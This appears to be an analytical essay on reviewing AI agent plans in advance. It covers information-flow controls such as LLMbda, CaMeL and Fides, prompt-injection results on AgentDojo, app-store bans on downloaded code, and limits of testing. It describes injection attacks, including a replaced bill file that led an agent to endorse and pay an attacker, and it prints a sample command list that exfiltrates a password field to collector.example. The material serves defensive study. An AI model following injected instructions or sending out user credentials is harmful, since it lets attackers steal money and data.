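For a wealthy customer, the third line sets `test` to false, so the program skips the assignment on the fourth. CaMeL labels a variable only when an assignment to it runs, so `rich` still counts as public and the email goes out. For any other customer, the email doesn't go out, so the stranger learns something about the balance either way. LLMbda prevents this leak because its ordinary variables never change. The conversation can change, but the interpreter blocks additions to a public conversation inside a branch that depends on a secret.

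### What noninterference guarantees

*Noninterference* is the property that changing untrusted data cannot change any trusted result. If two runs of the email program differ only in the text of the incoming message, the recipient may differ, but the subject and body must be the same. The same property protects secrets, since changing a secret cannot change any public result.

Language models complicate this because their answers are partly random, so two runs can differ by chance. Garby and colleagues therefore compare probabilities. Let μ(x) and ν(x) be the probabilities of a visible result x for two inputs that differ only in hidden data. Each set of probabilities can add up to less than 1, because the interpreter stops some runs and others never finish. The property requires a single distribution ω, with a total of at most 1, such that μ(x) ≤ ω(x) and ν(x) ≤ ω(x) for every x.

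If both programs always finish, μ and ν must be equal. Otherwise, they can differ by at most the average of the two probabilities of not finishing. For example, if each program fails to finish 2% of the time, they can differ by no more than two percentage points. This tolerance is small for one run, but it adds up if an attacker can try repeatedly. CaMeL's retry loop runs outside the part of the system that tracks labels, so an attacker could learn a whole secret one bit at a time by seeing which attempts the policy blocked.

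Garby and colleagues proved in Lean, a language for computer-checked proofs, that every LLMbda program has this property. The interpreter that calls the model is also a Lean function, and they proved that its results follow the same probabilities as the formal definition, provided the model's replies also match the definition's probabilities.

### Code that did not exist at review

The theorem covers every program in the language and every model. Like a havoc proof, it needs no assumption about what the model replies, so it holds even when the reply is code nobody has seen. The interpreter runs that code under the label of the conversation that produced it. If the conversation contains an untrusted email, everything the code computes is also untrusted, and a tool that requires trusted input will reject it.

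Earlier proofs of this kind cut every part that handles hidden data out of the program's text and showed that the remainder behaves the same for both inputs. This is impossible when part of the text arrives during the run. Garby and colleagues instead defined a second way of running a program, which skips a computation as soon as its label becomes hidden and puts an empty value in its place. This version behaves identically for both inputs and produces each visible result at least as often as the real program does, so its probabilities can serve as ω.

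Unlike ELBA, LLMbda has no types and does all its checking during the run, so a job can stop partway. As with ELBA's library, a reviewer still has to read the tools, because the protection depends on them to label outside data correctly.

### Endorsement

Many jobs need untrusted data to affect what happens. In the refund script, the customer wrote the ticket, so the model's answer is untrusted, and a strict version of `pay` would reject every refund. LLMbda handles this with an explicit step, `endorse`, which relabels an untrusted value as trusted.

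In one example from Garby and colleagues, a model sorts an incoming email into one of a few fixed categories, and the program endorses the category and uses it as the subject of a reply. With eight categories, an attacker could choose any of the eight subjects but couldn't write a new one. The refund script could endorse a whole number from 0 to 50 in the same way. A second theorem limits the damage by guaranteeing that secrets stay protected however a program uses `endorse`.

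If a model has read untrusted text in a conversation, the code it writes there runs as untrusted and `endorse` has no effect, so an attacker can't endorse text just by getting the model to write `endorse`. The danger arises when an earlier step has already endorsed the attacker's text. Code that a model writes from that text then runs as trusted, and its own endorsements work. Garby and colleagues sketch a stricter version that marks each endorsed value so it can't be endorsed again, and another that accepts only values from a fixed list. They haven't yet proved how much protection these add.

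A reviewer can search a plan for the word `endorse`. Each occurrence marks a place where the plan lets outside data through, and a long plan might contain only two or three. However, in the agent that Garby and colleagues tested, a model writes the endorsements into its plan, though it does so before seeing any untrusted data. Someone who approved only the surrounding agent would never see those endorsements. Garby and colleagues mention, as future work, checking such plans before execution, which is what Meijer proposes.

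### The banking test

The agent, RANDORI, asks a model to write a plan and tests it on mock data, where payments do nothing and every file contains the same placeholder text. If the plan fails, the model sees the error and tries again, so it can correct mistakes without reading anything an attacker could have written. The model then writes a final version, which runs once on the real account. The practice runs don't test the labels, so a plan can pass them and still stop partway through the real job.

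Garby and colleagues used the banking part of AgentDojo, which has 16 tasks and nine attacks on each. With three models and three repetitions, that makes 1,296 attacked runs. The table shows the results for MiMo-v2.5, the only model they ran in all four settings. It leaves out the CaMeL runs that didn't finish.

| MiMo-v2.5 | Tasks completed, no attack | Tasks completed, under attack | Attacks that succeeded |
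|---|---|---|---|
| RANDORI | 64.6% | 59.5% | 0 of 432 |
| RANDORI without `endorse` | 54.2% | 56.2% | 0 of 432 |
| CaMeL, policies off | 70.8% | 72.2% | 4 of 382 |
| CaMeL, policies on | 37.5% | 41.5% | 0 of 357 |

RANDORI completed far more tasks than CaMeL did with its policies on, partly because RANDORI's rules are laxer. It enforces only some of CaMeL's policies and lets its planner endorse data. Garby and colleagues also say RANDORI matched CaMeL when CaMeL's policies were off. That is fair for the runs without attacks, where the margins of error exceed 20 percentage points, but under attack CaMeL was nearly 13 points ahead with this model.

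The number of blocked attacks makes every system that plans before reading data look better than it is. In 97 of the 144 combinations of task and attack, the attack needs an action that an ordinary plan for the task wouldn't contain, such as a payment in a plan that only summarises transactions. The labels matter mainly in the other 47, which account for 423 of RANDORI's 1,296 runs.

Even the easy cases aren't entirely safe without labels. In one task, the agent has to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. With policies off, CaMeL's planner twice wrote a loop with a branch for each tool, and the file's contents determined which branch ran. Every action was in the plan, so control-flow integrity held even though the plan carried out whatever instructions the attacker wrote.

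Two attacks succeeded against RANDORI, both with GPT-5.2 on the same task. The user asks the agent to read a text file and make the payment it describes, and the attacker replaces the file's contents with a different payment request. The payment tool accepts only a trusted recipient, so the plan has to endorse the recipient named in the file. In both attacks, the plan endorsed the attacker as the recipient, and the payment went through.

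This doesn't contradict the theorem. The guarantee against untrusted data is unconditional only for plans without `endorse`, and the theorem for plans with `endorse` protects secrets, which this attack didn't touch. Without `endorse`, the interpreter blocks both the attack and the honest payment. The other two models had no such failures, but if their plans also endorsed the recipient, the theorem doesn't explain why. Those models may simply have failed at the task.

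### Truthfulness and judgment

These proofs leave out much of what people want from an agent. The refund proof holds even if the money goes to the wrong customers. A PocketFlow agent can stay in its folder, use only approved tools and still write a false report.

Moon and Varshney acknowledge that truthfulness, deception and manipulation are outside their scope. But they argue that many of the worst outcomes, such as stealing data, deleting files or making irreversible payments, require an action that crosses a boundary, and that a proof can cover these outcomes however capable the model becomes. They compare such a proof to the control rods of a nuclear reactor, which drop by gravity when the active controls fail. They suggest other methods for the content a model writes, including statistical bounds on how often it produces a bad output.

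This is a reasonable division of labour, but the boundary is less clear when a person acts on what the agent writes. Franco and Gershenson compare a chatbot's user to an interpreter that receives a harmful program as data. If Michelle makes a payment because of a false summary, the payment never passes through the agent's interface.

Garby and colleagues regard the two successful payments as showing the limit of what data tracking can do. To stop the payments, the agent would have to judge from the words in the file that the request was suspicious. They also note that CaMeL's original evaluation included a successful attack on the same task. In their view, the user's request to pay the bill justifies trusting the file that contains it.

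That justification is convincing if only the user can edit the file. In the test, somebody else had replaced its contents, and the user had presumably meant to pay the original bill. Garby and colleagues present `endorse` as a programmable form of asking the user to confirm, but a model wrote these endorsements and no person saw them. For payments, the plan could stop at the `endorse` step and show the recipient and amount to the user, who might then notice that the account doesn't belong to the electricity company.

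## App stores that forbid code arriving after review

LLMbda lets unreviewed code run but limits what it can affect. Apple and Google mostly forbid such code in their stores. Both companies were reviewing software for release long before agents wrote plans. An approved app may stay on millions of devices for years, so both had to decide what an approval covers if the software can change afterwards.

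Guideline 2.5.2 of Apple's *App Review Guidelines* requires an app to be self-contained in its bundle, the package that the developer submits. The app may not download, install or execute code that "introduces or changes features or functionality of the app, including other apps". Without such a rule, a weather app could fetch new code the day after approval and become a gambling app. The new code could also use any access the user had already granted the app, such as a photo editor's permission to open the picture library.

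A related rule for Mac apps states the purpose more directly by forbidding downloads of code or resources that would significantly change an app from the version Apple reviewed. In TechRepublic's *The Hidden Problem With ‘Vibe Coding’ Apps on Apple’s App Store*, an Apple representative gives the same reason for enforcing 2.5.2. Apple also applies 2.5.2 to iPhone apps that people in the European Union and Japan get from other marketplaces, so a developer can't avoid it by leaving the App Store.

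The guideline itself makes one exception, for apps that teach programming or let students test code. In limited circumstances, these apps may download code if the user can view and edit all of it. In effect, the user replaces Apple as the reviewer. That makes sense for a student learning Python, but not for someone who wants a finished app because they can't program.

Guideline 4.7 makes a wider exception, letting an app offer chatbots, plug-ins, streaming games, and small apps and games written in web languages, even though they aren't in the bundle. The developer is responsible for all of this software and must give Apple an index with links to each item. The software can't use the phone's own functions without Apple's permission, and the user must consent each time the app shares data with it.

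Apple's licence agreement with developers has a looser test for downloaded code. The agreement, as quoted in 9to5Mac's *Developers behind vibe coding app Anything detail next steps*, lets an app download interpreted code, such as JavaScript, if the code doesn't add features inconsistent with the app's "intended and advertised purpose". A new feature that suits the advertised purpose would pass this test but could still break 2.5.2, which forbids code that introduces any feature. In 2026, this difference mattered a great deal to apps advertised as tools for making other apps.

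### Replit, Vibecode and Anything

"Vibe coding" means describing a program in ordinary words and letting a model write it. Replit, Vibecode and Anything offered iPhone apps for this, and users could try out the generated programs on their phones. Apple had reviewed these apps but not the programs they generated.

Anything's iPhone app came out in November 2025 without trouble. The company says Apple began blocking its updates in December under guideline 2.5.2, then rejected four different technical fixes. Replit published an update in January, then none for four months.

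The dispute became public in March, when Palazzolo and Tilley's *Apple Cracks Down on 'Vibe Coding' Apps* reported in The Information that Apple was holding back updates to Replit and Vibecode. Most of what is known about the negotiations comes from that report and its unnamed sources. As summarized in MacRumors' *Apple Quietly Blocks Updates for Popular 'Vibe Coding' Apps* (2026), Apple seemed to object to Replit showing generated apps in a web view, a browser window embedded in Replit's own app. The sources expected Apple to approve an update that opened the generated apps in an outside browser. Apple's reviewers had indicated that they would probably approve Vibecode's update if Vibecode stopped generating software for Apple devices.

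Replit had argued that the generated code ran on a separate virtual machine and that its app only displayed the result, much as a social media app displays a linked page. Apple's reviewers at first rejected this argument, according to The Decoder's *Apple reportedly blocks vibe-coding apps from publishing updates*, which also draws on The Information. Apple told MacRumors that it had no rule against vibe coding and pointed to guideline 2.5.2.

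Anything's co-founder, Dhruv Amin, then submitted an update that moved previews to a web browser, the change that was supposed to satisfy Apple in Replit's case. Apple blocked the update and removed the whole app on 26 March, according to MacRumors' *Apple Pulls Vibe Coding App 'Anything' From App Store, Escalating Enforcement* (2026), which again relies on The Information. The app returned on 3 April, but AppleInsider's *Vibe coding app's victory lap cut very short by the App Store* reported that it was gone again by 6 April.

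The Financial Times later saw messages between Apple and Anything, which Landymore summarises in *Apple Is Blocking Vibe Coding Apps From the App Store, Infuriating Developers*. Apple told Anything that letting users preview their apps counted as downloading code. When Anything removed the previews, Apple rejected the app for offering too little functionality. A developer could reasonably conclude from those two answers that no version of the app would pass.

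iClarified's *Replit CEO Says Apple's App Store Block Justification Is a 'Total Lie'* (2026) reports that Replit's chief executive, Amjad Masad, told an audience at the end of April that Apple's justification was a lie and that Replit was prepared to go to court. On 15 May, Masad announced that Replit had "worked things out with Apple" and released an update. According to AppleInsider's *Apple's treatment of AI coding apps could be shifting with Replit update* (2026), neither company said whether the previews had changed. The company Anything moved part of its service to text messages and started building a desktop program for previews.

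Apple last revised its guidelines on 16 October, and its list of changes doesn't mention guideline 2.5.2. Replit can update its app again, but other developers still can't tell from public information which kind of preview Apple accepts.

### Complaints about enforcement and competition

Developers complain that Apple enforces the rule unevenly. Vercel's v0, which has similar features, kept publishing updates throughout. Apple approved an update to Emergent, another vibe-coding app, the same week it removed Anything. Gizchina's *Apple Pulls Vibe Coding App 'Anything'* describes the two apps' workflows as identical. Apple also approved Lovable's app while Replit was still waiting.

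The Information reported that Apple also left the old versions of the blocked apps in the store. *Updates to Vibe Coding Apps Rejected From the App Store* (2026) asks why Apple would block only the updates if the apps had been breaking a long-standing rule. The old versions presumably ran generated code too, so blocking updates did little to protect existing users. One innocent explanation is that reviewers mostly look at an app when its developer submits something. But blocking updates also keeps developers from fixing bugs, which puts pressure on them to agree to changes, whether or not Apple intended this.

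Critics also suspect a commercial motive. Vibe-coding apps compete with Xcode, Apple's programming tool, which now includes AI features from Anthropic and OpenAI. The apps also make web apps that people can use without the App Store. Gene Burrus, a competition lawyer, told The Information that Apple has a history of blocking apps that compete on its platform. David George of Andreessen Horowitz, a venture capital firm that has invested in Replit, said that security was not a good reason for the restrictions, according to heise's *Vibe-Coding*.

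Neither motive alone easily explains Apple's request to Vibecode. If Apple mainly feared losing business to the web, it would have more reason to object to web apps than to apps for its own devices, which still need its approval to enter the store. Security might be a reason if previews of apps for Apple devices could use the phone's own functions through Vibecode, but Apple hasn't publicly said so.

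Apple says 2.5.2 is old and doesn't single out vibe coding. According to PYMNTS's *Apple’s Vibe Coding App Curb Leaves Startups Frustrated*, Apple told the Financial Times that its review process protects users' privacy and security, and denied that a rise in AI-generated apps had slowed approvals. Apple also said it had stayed in regular contact about the violations with the developer in The Information's report. Masad said Replit had submitted build after build without getting clear feedback.

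Apple's position has some support elsewhere in the guidelines, which allow apps made with an app-generation service if whoever supplies the content submits the app. Amin says people have used Anything to publish thousands of apps in the store. The same generated code could therefore break the rules as a preview and later pass review as a finished app. Apple can answer that someone would have checked the code by then.

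But Apple doesn't require review of everything that runs on an iPhone. For an app meant only for family and friends, Apple suggests in its guidelines using Xcode to install it on a device for free. Someone with a Mac can run an unreviewed app on their own phone, while someone with only the phone can't preview the same app inside Anything. The person with the Mac has at least chosen to install that particular program, but the person who asked Anything to make it has, in a sense, chosen it too.

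### Chrome's ban on remotely hosted code

Google has a similar rule for Chrome extensions, small programs that add features to the browser and can often read and change the pages a user visits. With Manifest V3, the current extension format, Google banned remotely hosted code. All the code an extension runs must be in the package submitted to the Chrome Web Store, and a reviewer must be able to tell from that package what the extension does. An extension can't load a script from a server or pass a downloaded string to `eval`.

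An app can still download data. Google's policy allows images, synchronised account data and a remote configuration file that turns features on or off, as long as all the logic for those features is in the package. A reviewer can't try every combination of features but can read the code for each feature.

A developer could try to get around the rule by sending instructions in the form of data. Suppose an extension downloads this list:

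```
[["find", "password field"],
 ["read", "its contents"],
 ["send", "collector.example"]]
```

A JSON reader won't execute any of this list, but if the extension contains a loop that looks up each command and performs the matching action, the list is a program and the loop is its interpreter. Google's policy prohibits building an interpreter to run complex commands from a remote source, even if the commands arrive as data. Apple's guideline 2.5.2 has no such clause and refers only to code, although Apple could argue that a list like this is code.

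Google's ban also has an exception for extensions whose purpose is to run scripts that users write or choose themselves. Such extensions may do this through a dedicated browser interface, which the user has to switch on.

The word "complex" leaves some doubt about where configuration ends and an interpreter begins. A file that turns on a dark theme is clearly configuration, while one containing the instruction "if the page contains a price, copy it, then open the next page and repeat" is clearly a program. Many real configuration files fall between the two, with conditional rules such as showing a banner only if the user is in France and hasn't yet paid.

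### When a model's answer is data

The original refund script and the version with four branches would pass both rules if they were part of an app, because all their code is in the package. An app that ran Python returned by the model would probably break Apple's rule, and an extension that did the same would break Google's.

The version in which the model can use the refund tool is harder to classify. By the end of a run, the model's tool calls amount to a program that no reviewer saw and that a loop in the package interpreted. Google's clause on interpreters, read strictly, seems to forbid this. Yet the Chrome Web Store carries browser agents that work this way, including one from Anthropic. Google presumably treats the available actions as the extension's logic and the model's replies as input. The developer of the password-stealing extension could describe its list the same way, so the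 distinction seems to depend on what Google thinks the extension is for.

Both rules also apply only to code on the user's device. An app can send a request to a server where a model writes and runs a new program, then receive the result as data. If that program moves money between accounts, the user may lose as much as if it had run on the phone. Conversely, a recursive language model in an isolated interpreter on the phone might only search a document and return a paragraph, but it would have to run generated code to do that.

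The line between code and data is therefore a poor guide to how much harm a change can do, but banning downloaded code still limits what an app can do. An app that runs only the code in its package has control-flow integrity, so a model's answer can't make it read contacts if the package has no code for that. This guarantee is weak if the package already contains an action as general as the shell command in the PocketFlow example. A scanner can also search a package for calls that run downloaded code, but it can't tell whether a server's future answers will be harmful.

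Apple's October revision concerned a kind of change that can fall entirely outside 2.5.2. A photo app might send each picture to a server and display the edited version that comes back. After approval, its operator could switch the server to a model that produces fake nude images of the people in the pictures. The app and server would still exchange only pictures, so no code would reach the phone.

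*Apple's App Store rules now require apps to remove AI intimate imagery* (Rijo, 2026) describes a new guideline, 2.5.19, against apps that behave one way during review and another after approval. Apple gave "nudification" apps as its example and said its rules already banned hidden features. The older guideline 2.3.1 does ban them, and it requires developers to describe each new feature specifically enough for a reviewer to test it.

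These rules differ from 2.5.2, whose ban on downloaded code is meant to ensure that the package contains everything the app can do. That ban fits the every-run reading of approval. Guideline 2.5.19 fits the expected-run reading, because Apple applies it by comparing the app's later behaviour with what the reviewers understood it to be. Apple can therefore enforce it only after somebody notices a difference.

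Apple's reviewers also rely on expectations about an app's behavior more than the wording of 2.5.2 suggests, because they try out the app as part of the review. Apple tells developers to provide a demo account and keep their servers running during the review. If the app uses a remote model, the reviewer sees a few of the model's answers and has to guess at the rest. After approval, the developer can replace the model without submitting anything to Apple.

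### Limiting access instead of banning code

Apple could instead build on guideline 4.7, which already accepts software from outside the bundle and restricts what it can reach. LACUNA similarly limits the capabilities available to generated code. A rule for previews could let generated code run in a web view with no access to the phone's own functions, the surrounding app's data or the user's saved passwords. An app that gave the preview that access would fail review, whatever the preview contained.

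That would answer much of the security concern about Replit's previews, if they worked as Replit described. The previews still wouldn't fit easily under the current guideline 4.7, which requires an index of all the software on offer, because a preview doesn't exist until a user asks for it. Apple would have to accept a description of what previews can access instead of a list of them.

Limits on access wouldn't stop every kind of harm either. A generated program that can only draw on the screen could still imitate a bank's login page and ask for a password. Apple's preference for an outside browser makes some sense for this reason, because a browser normally shows a page's address, while an embedded view may not. A user who looks at the address might notice that the page doesn't belong to the bank.

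## Estimating from the code how much is left open

Apple and Google decide what needs another review mainly based on whether new code has arrived. For a plan that calls a model, a reviewer might prefer a number, calculated from the code, that measures how much the plan leaves open. The simplest candidate is the number of possible outcomes.

### Counting outcomes and paths

Suppose the refund script is changed so that the model only answers yes or no to each of the 20 tickets, and each yes pays $50. There are then 2²⁰ possible lists of answers, or about a million. Each answer carries at most one bit, so the 20 answers carry at most 20 bits. The original script allows 51²⁰ possible lists, which comes to 113 bits. By this measure the original leaves far more open, but both scripts can pay out at most $1,000.

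| What the model decides | Possible outcomes | Bits | Largest loss |
|---|---|---|---|
| 20 yes/no answers on $50 refunds | about 1 million | 20 | $1,000 |
| 20 refunds of 0 to 50 whole dollars | about 1.4 × 10³⁴ | 113 | $1,000 |
| One yes/no answer on a $250,000 loan | 2 | 1 | $250,000 |

The number of bits also depends on how likely each answer is. If only one ticket in a hundred gets a yes from the model, each answer carries about 0.08 bits on average, and all 20 carry 1.6. This lower figure is a better estimate for ordinary use, but the wrong one for an attacker who writes the tickets and may be able to get 20 yeses.

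Another problem with counting the paths through a program is that the result depends on how the branches are arranged. Suppose a plan has 40 two-way branches, the average for the NOVA plans in *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*. If the branches form a tree whose paths never rejoin, each branch adds one path, and the plan has 41. If the branches follow one another and the two sides of each rejoin before the next, each branch can double the number of paths, so the plan has up to 2⁴⁰, or about 1.1 trillion.

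The plan with a trillion paths may still be the easier one to review. If each branch decides whether one of 40 news items goes into a newsletter, the reviewer only needs to read the 40 items, because no choice affects another. Combinations matter when an early branch changes something that a later one uses. For example, one branch might replace an email address, and a later one might send a file to it. A reviewer who checked each branch separately could find both harmless.

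### Why Fides trusts short answers

Bits are a better measure of how much an attacker could write into an answer. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) uses them this way in Fides, the step-by-step planner that Foerster and colleagues adapted for computer use. Fides keeps untrusted text in variables that the planning model can't see. The planner can query an isolated model about the text and specify the type of the answer. Fides ranks types by how much information they can carry, with yes/no lowest, then a choice from a short list, then free text. A policy can let a yes/no answer from an untrusted email influence the next action but forbid free text from doing so.

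For example, a user asks the agent to read three emails and create a calendar event if one of them requests a meeting. The planner needs only a yes or no. If it read the emails itself, it could encounter an instruction to forward the mailbox, which a yes or no can't contain. Costa and colleagues argue that a policy may accept the answer because it gives the untrusted text only one bit of influence.

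However, one bit is enough to choose between two actions, one of which may be harmful. In the water-filter example, a false yes makes the plan buy the filter for $400. In the meeting example, anyone who can email the user can get a yes by asking for a meeting, and the isolated model then takes the event details from the same email. An unwanted calendar entry does little damage, but if the plan made a payment instead, the same bit could cost the user a lot of money.

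The information in short answers also accumulates, as the leaked bits did in CaMeL's retry loop. A planner could reconstruct a hidden text by asking about eight yes/no questions per letter. Garby and colleagues add that when Fides lets a short answer through, a reviewer can't tell from the run whether it was a leak or the harmless answer the policy's author meant to allow.

Fides stopped every attack in AgentDojo with its policies switched on, but this doesn't show that short answers are safe, because Costa and colleagues left the restriction on answer types out of the version they tested. They did so because most AgentDojo tasks don't need it. They classify 44% of the banking tasks and 43% of the Slack tasks as ones where the right steps depend on what the data contains, so those would be good places to test the restriction.

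*Preventing Prompt Injection with Type-Directed Privilege Separation* (Jacob, Alghamdi and colleagues, 2025) tested a similar restriction. In its design, a model that reads untrusted text can influence the acting model only through numbers, yes/no answers and choices from a fixed list. The shopping agent, for example, receives two scores from 0 to 10 for each customer review, which rate how strongly the review supports the product and how relevant it is. Instructions hidden in the reviews never succeeded. But the paper excludes attacks that use false or misleading data, so the test doesn't cover a customer who lies in a review.

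The shopping agent has some protection against such lies because it uses the median score. If nine honest reviews score 2 or 3 and a fake one scores 10, the median stays between 2 and 3. The median would protect the agent just as well if scores could go up to a million.

Their bug-fixing agent uses a short answer in a way that would suit advance review. A planning model that has not read the bug report writes three repair plans, and a model that has read it returns only the number of the best one. An attacker can influence the choice but can't add a fourth plan. A reviewer could read all three and judge whether the worst would be acceptable. The branch constraints that Zingrillo and colleagues use in COBRA serve a similar purpose.

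### Scoring autonomy from the code

Cihon, Stein and colleagues (2025) rate the whole agent instead of its separate answers. In *Measuring AI agent autonomy*, they propose scoring how independently an agent can act by inspecting its orchestration code, the software that connects the model to its tools. This saves money and avoids accidents during testing because nobody has to run the agent. They tried the method on AutoGen, a popular open-source framework for building agents, and rated five attributes at three levels each. The table gives the two extremes.

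| Attribute | Least autonomy | Most autonomy |
|---|---|---|
| Actions | Conversation only | Can run any code |
| Environment | Limits on internet access, memory and computing power | Open access to the internet and the host machine |
| Orchestration | Fixed order of interactions | No limit on interactions |
| Human involvement | Always consults the user | Never consults the user |
| Observability | Dashboards or explanations for the user | No logs |

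Many of the scores come from settings that a program could look up. For example, an agent gets the top score for actions unless its code turns off code execution, and the top score for human involvement if `human_input_mode` is `NEVER`.

Three researchers scored ten AutoGen applications. Eight received the top score for actions, seven for environment and seven for human involvement. The researchers' agreement was 0.64 overall but only 0.30 for actions, on a scale where 0 is the agreement expected by chance and 1 is complete agreement. The low agreement on actions is a serious weakness, since the actions available to an agent largely determine the harm it can do. Cihon and colleagues explain that developers can write their own tools or add other frameworks, which complicates the review.

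Inspecting the code also misses behaviour that appears only in complex environments, how the agent adapts to users, and how its actions change the conditions it later works in. The five attributes leave out how specific the agent's goals are and what it does when something fails.

The levels are too coarse for approving a single plan. The original refund script and the version that gives an agent the refund tool would both get the middle score for actions because both use a ready-made tool, even though the script can lose at most $1,000 and the agent can empty the account. The method seems better suited to surveying large numbers of agents with little effort. In the pilot, most developers had kept AutoGen's default settings, but one application, Composio, consistently overrode the default and ran generated code outside a protective container. A survey could find every project that does this.

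### Checking every route through a workflow

*Agentproof* reports specific faults instead of a score. It represents a workflow as a graph and runs six structural checks on it. Each node is a step, such as a model call, a tool, a choice of route or a human approval. In one example, a developer adds a step that drafts replies to normal-priority emails but forgets to connect it to the step that sends them. The replies are never sent, and no error appears. A test run would reveal the fault only if it included a normal-priority email. The structural check finds the dead end in the graph and prints the route that leads to it.

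Users can also write rules about the order of steps, for example that a human review must follow an email draft. The software turns each rule into a small state machine, like Meijer's security automaton, and explores combinations of steps and states instead of following every path separately. A plan with 40 two-way branches in a row has about 120 steps and a trillion paths, but under a rule with three states, the software has at most 360 combinations to visit. In tests, the structural checks took about a tenth of a second on a graph with 5,000 steps.

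The analysis assumes that the workflow could take any branch at any point, much as havoc semantics lets a model return any value. If it finds no violation, no run of that workflow graph contains one. But it may report violations on routes that could never occur, such as one that treats the same order as both paid and unpaid.

The researchers tested the software on 18 workflows they had written themselves. Five had structural defects and ten broke a rule requiring human approval, which the paper gives as 27% and 55%. They warn that these aren't rates for real systems, because they deliberately included typical mistakes to see whether the software would find them.

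The human-approval figure is also hard to interpret. A workflow passes the basic check if its graph contains a human step anywhere, even on a route that never leads to a payment. But some of the ten workflows that failed did low-risk work that arguably needed no approval. A stricter optional check would help a reviewer more. It removes every human step from the graph and tests whether a sensitive tool is still reachable. If it is, some route reaches that tool without approval.

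For workflows built with LangGraph, the software identifies a human step by the word "human" in its name. It would treat a step called `ask_manager` as a model call, and would presumably treat a model call named `humanize_text` as human approval. The rules about order can also be less strict than they sound. As the paper defines it, a run breaks the rule that a review must follow a draft only if a second draft comes before the review. A run that drafts one email, sends it unreviewed and stops would pass.

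The graph doesn't include the text the model generates or the refund amount it sets, so the checks can't establish the refund script's $1,000 limit. If a workflow adds agents while it runs, somebody also has to check the new graph.

### Running the same plan again

A reviewer could instead run the plan several times and see how much the results vary. *Agentproof* generated ten random routes through each of its workflows. In one workflow, none of the ten skipped the human review, although the graph analysis had found a route that did.

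Results can vary even when the request stays the same. A language model normally picks each token partly at random. A setting called temperature controls how much, and at zero the model always takes the most probable token. Thinking Machines Lab's *Defeating Nondeterminism in LLM Inference*, from September 2025, describes sending "Tell me about Richard Feynman" 1,000 times at temperature zero to a large open model from the Qwen family. The model still produced 80 different answers. All 1,000 responses were identical for the first 102 tokens, after which 992 gave Feynman's birthplace as "Queens, New York" and eight as "New York City".

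The answers varied because of how busy the server was. A server handles several users' requests together, and the size of the group can change the order in which it adds numbers. Computers round as they add, so a different order can give a slightly different sum, which occasionally changes the most probable token. With software that kept the order fixed, all 1,000 answers were identical. In a speed test with a smaller model, fixing the order raised the time for 1,000 requests from 26 seconds to 42. LMSYS's *Towards Deterministic Inference in SGLang and Reproducible RL Training* (2025) reports a version with an average slowdown of about 34%.

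*Understanding and Mitigating Numerical Sources of Nondeterminism in LLM Inference* reports that changing the number or version of the graphics chips can also change a model's answers. Reasoning models are especially sensitive, because a small rounding difference near the start can lead to a different chain of thought.

Removing this variation would let a reviewer replay a refund run exactly and find out why a customer got $50. It wouldn't show what the model will do with tomorrow's tickets, which contain different text. An agent that chooses its own steps also reacts to what its tools return, and *Recursive Semantic Divergence for LLM Agent Consistency* (2026) points out that small differences in those results can lead it to take different steps even if the model is deterministic.

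*How Consistent Are LLM Agents?* (Yagubyan, 2026) measured how much whole jobs vary between runs. Six models attempted each of 19 tasks ten times at temperature 1, the usual setting, with simulated tools that always gave the same output for the same input. On a scale from 0 to 1, the similarity between runs was 0.87 for the sequence of tools but 0.69 for the arguments, the values passed to those tools. Argument similarity fell to 0.52 for vague requests. The models, which included GPT-4.1 and Claude Sonnet 4, are well behind today's, so the exact figures are probably out of date.

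Agents that used more consistent tool sequences were correct in 90.2% of runs, compared with 61.2% for the less consistent ones. Variation in the arguments did not predict failure, and Yagubyan calls it benign. That may be right for search phrases and date formats, but it may not be for the refund script, where the order of the steps is already fixed and the argument that varies is a sum of money.

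An average over whole runs doesn't show where the differences arise. *GraphACM* (2026) matches equivalent states across repeated runs and compares what the agent did next in each. For a plan under review, this could identify the deferred decisions on which the model is least consistent, where a designer might add a human check. But a measure of consistency wouldn't reveal a mistake that the model makes every time.

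### Why test runs can't prove a limit

A guaranteed property has to hold in every permitted run, and tests cover only some of them. Suppose the version of the refund script that gives an agent the refund tool never pays more than $50 on a ticket in 1,000 independent test runs. If the share of runs with an overpayment is p, the chance of seeing none is (1 − p)¹⁰⁰⁰. This is 5% when p is about 0.3%, so the tester can say with 95% confidence only that the share is below about 0.3%. If the company runs the script 10,000 times a year, up to about 30 runs could still include an overpayment.

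Smaller samples are more likely to miss rare answers. In the Feynman test, "New York City" appeared in 0.8% of the answers. If each request independently had a 0.8% chance of producing it, a tester who sent only 100 requests would have a 45% chance of never seeing it.

The calculation also assumes that future runs will resemble the tests. A new model or a different group of customers could change the rate, and an attacker will look for inputs the tests didn't cover. If one wording in a million makes the agent overpay, 1,000 random tickets will almost certainly miss it, but an attacker who finds it can use it repeatedly. The range check in the original script stops the overpayment regardless of the ticket's wording.

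A single test run can disprove a limit, since one payment of $400 shows that the agent can exceed $50. Test runs can also show what a proof can't, such as how much the script usually pays and how often the model rejects a genuine complaint. This would help a reviewer set the total at which the script stops to call a person. If a replay of 200 past days with payments switched off gave totals from $120 to $260, the $300 limit suggested earlier would probably interrupt few ordinary runs.
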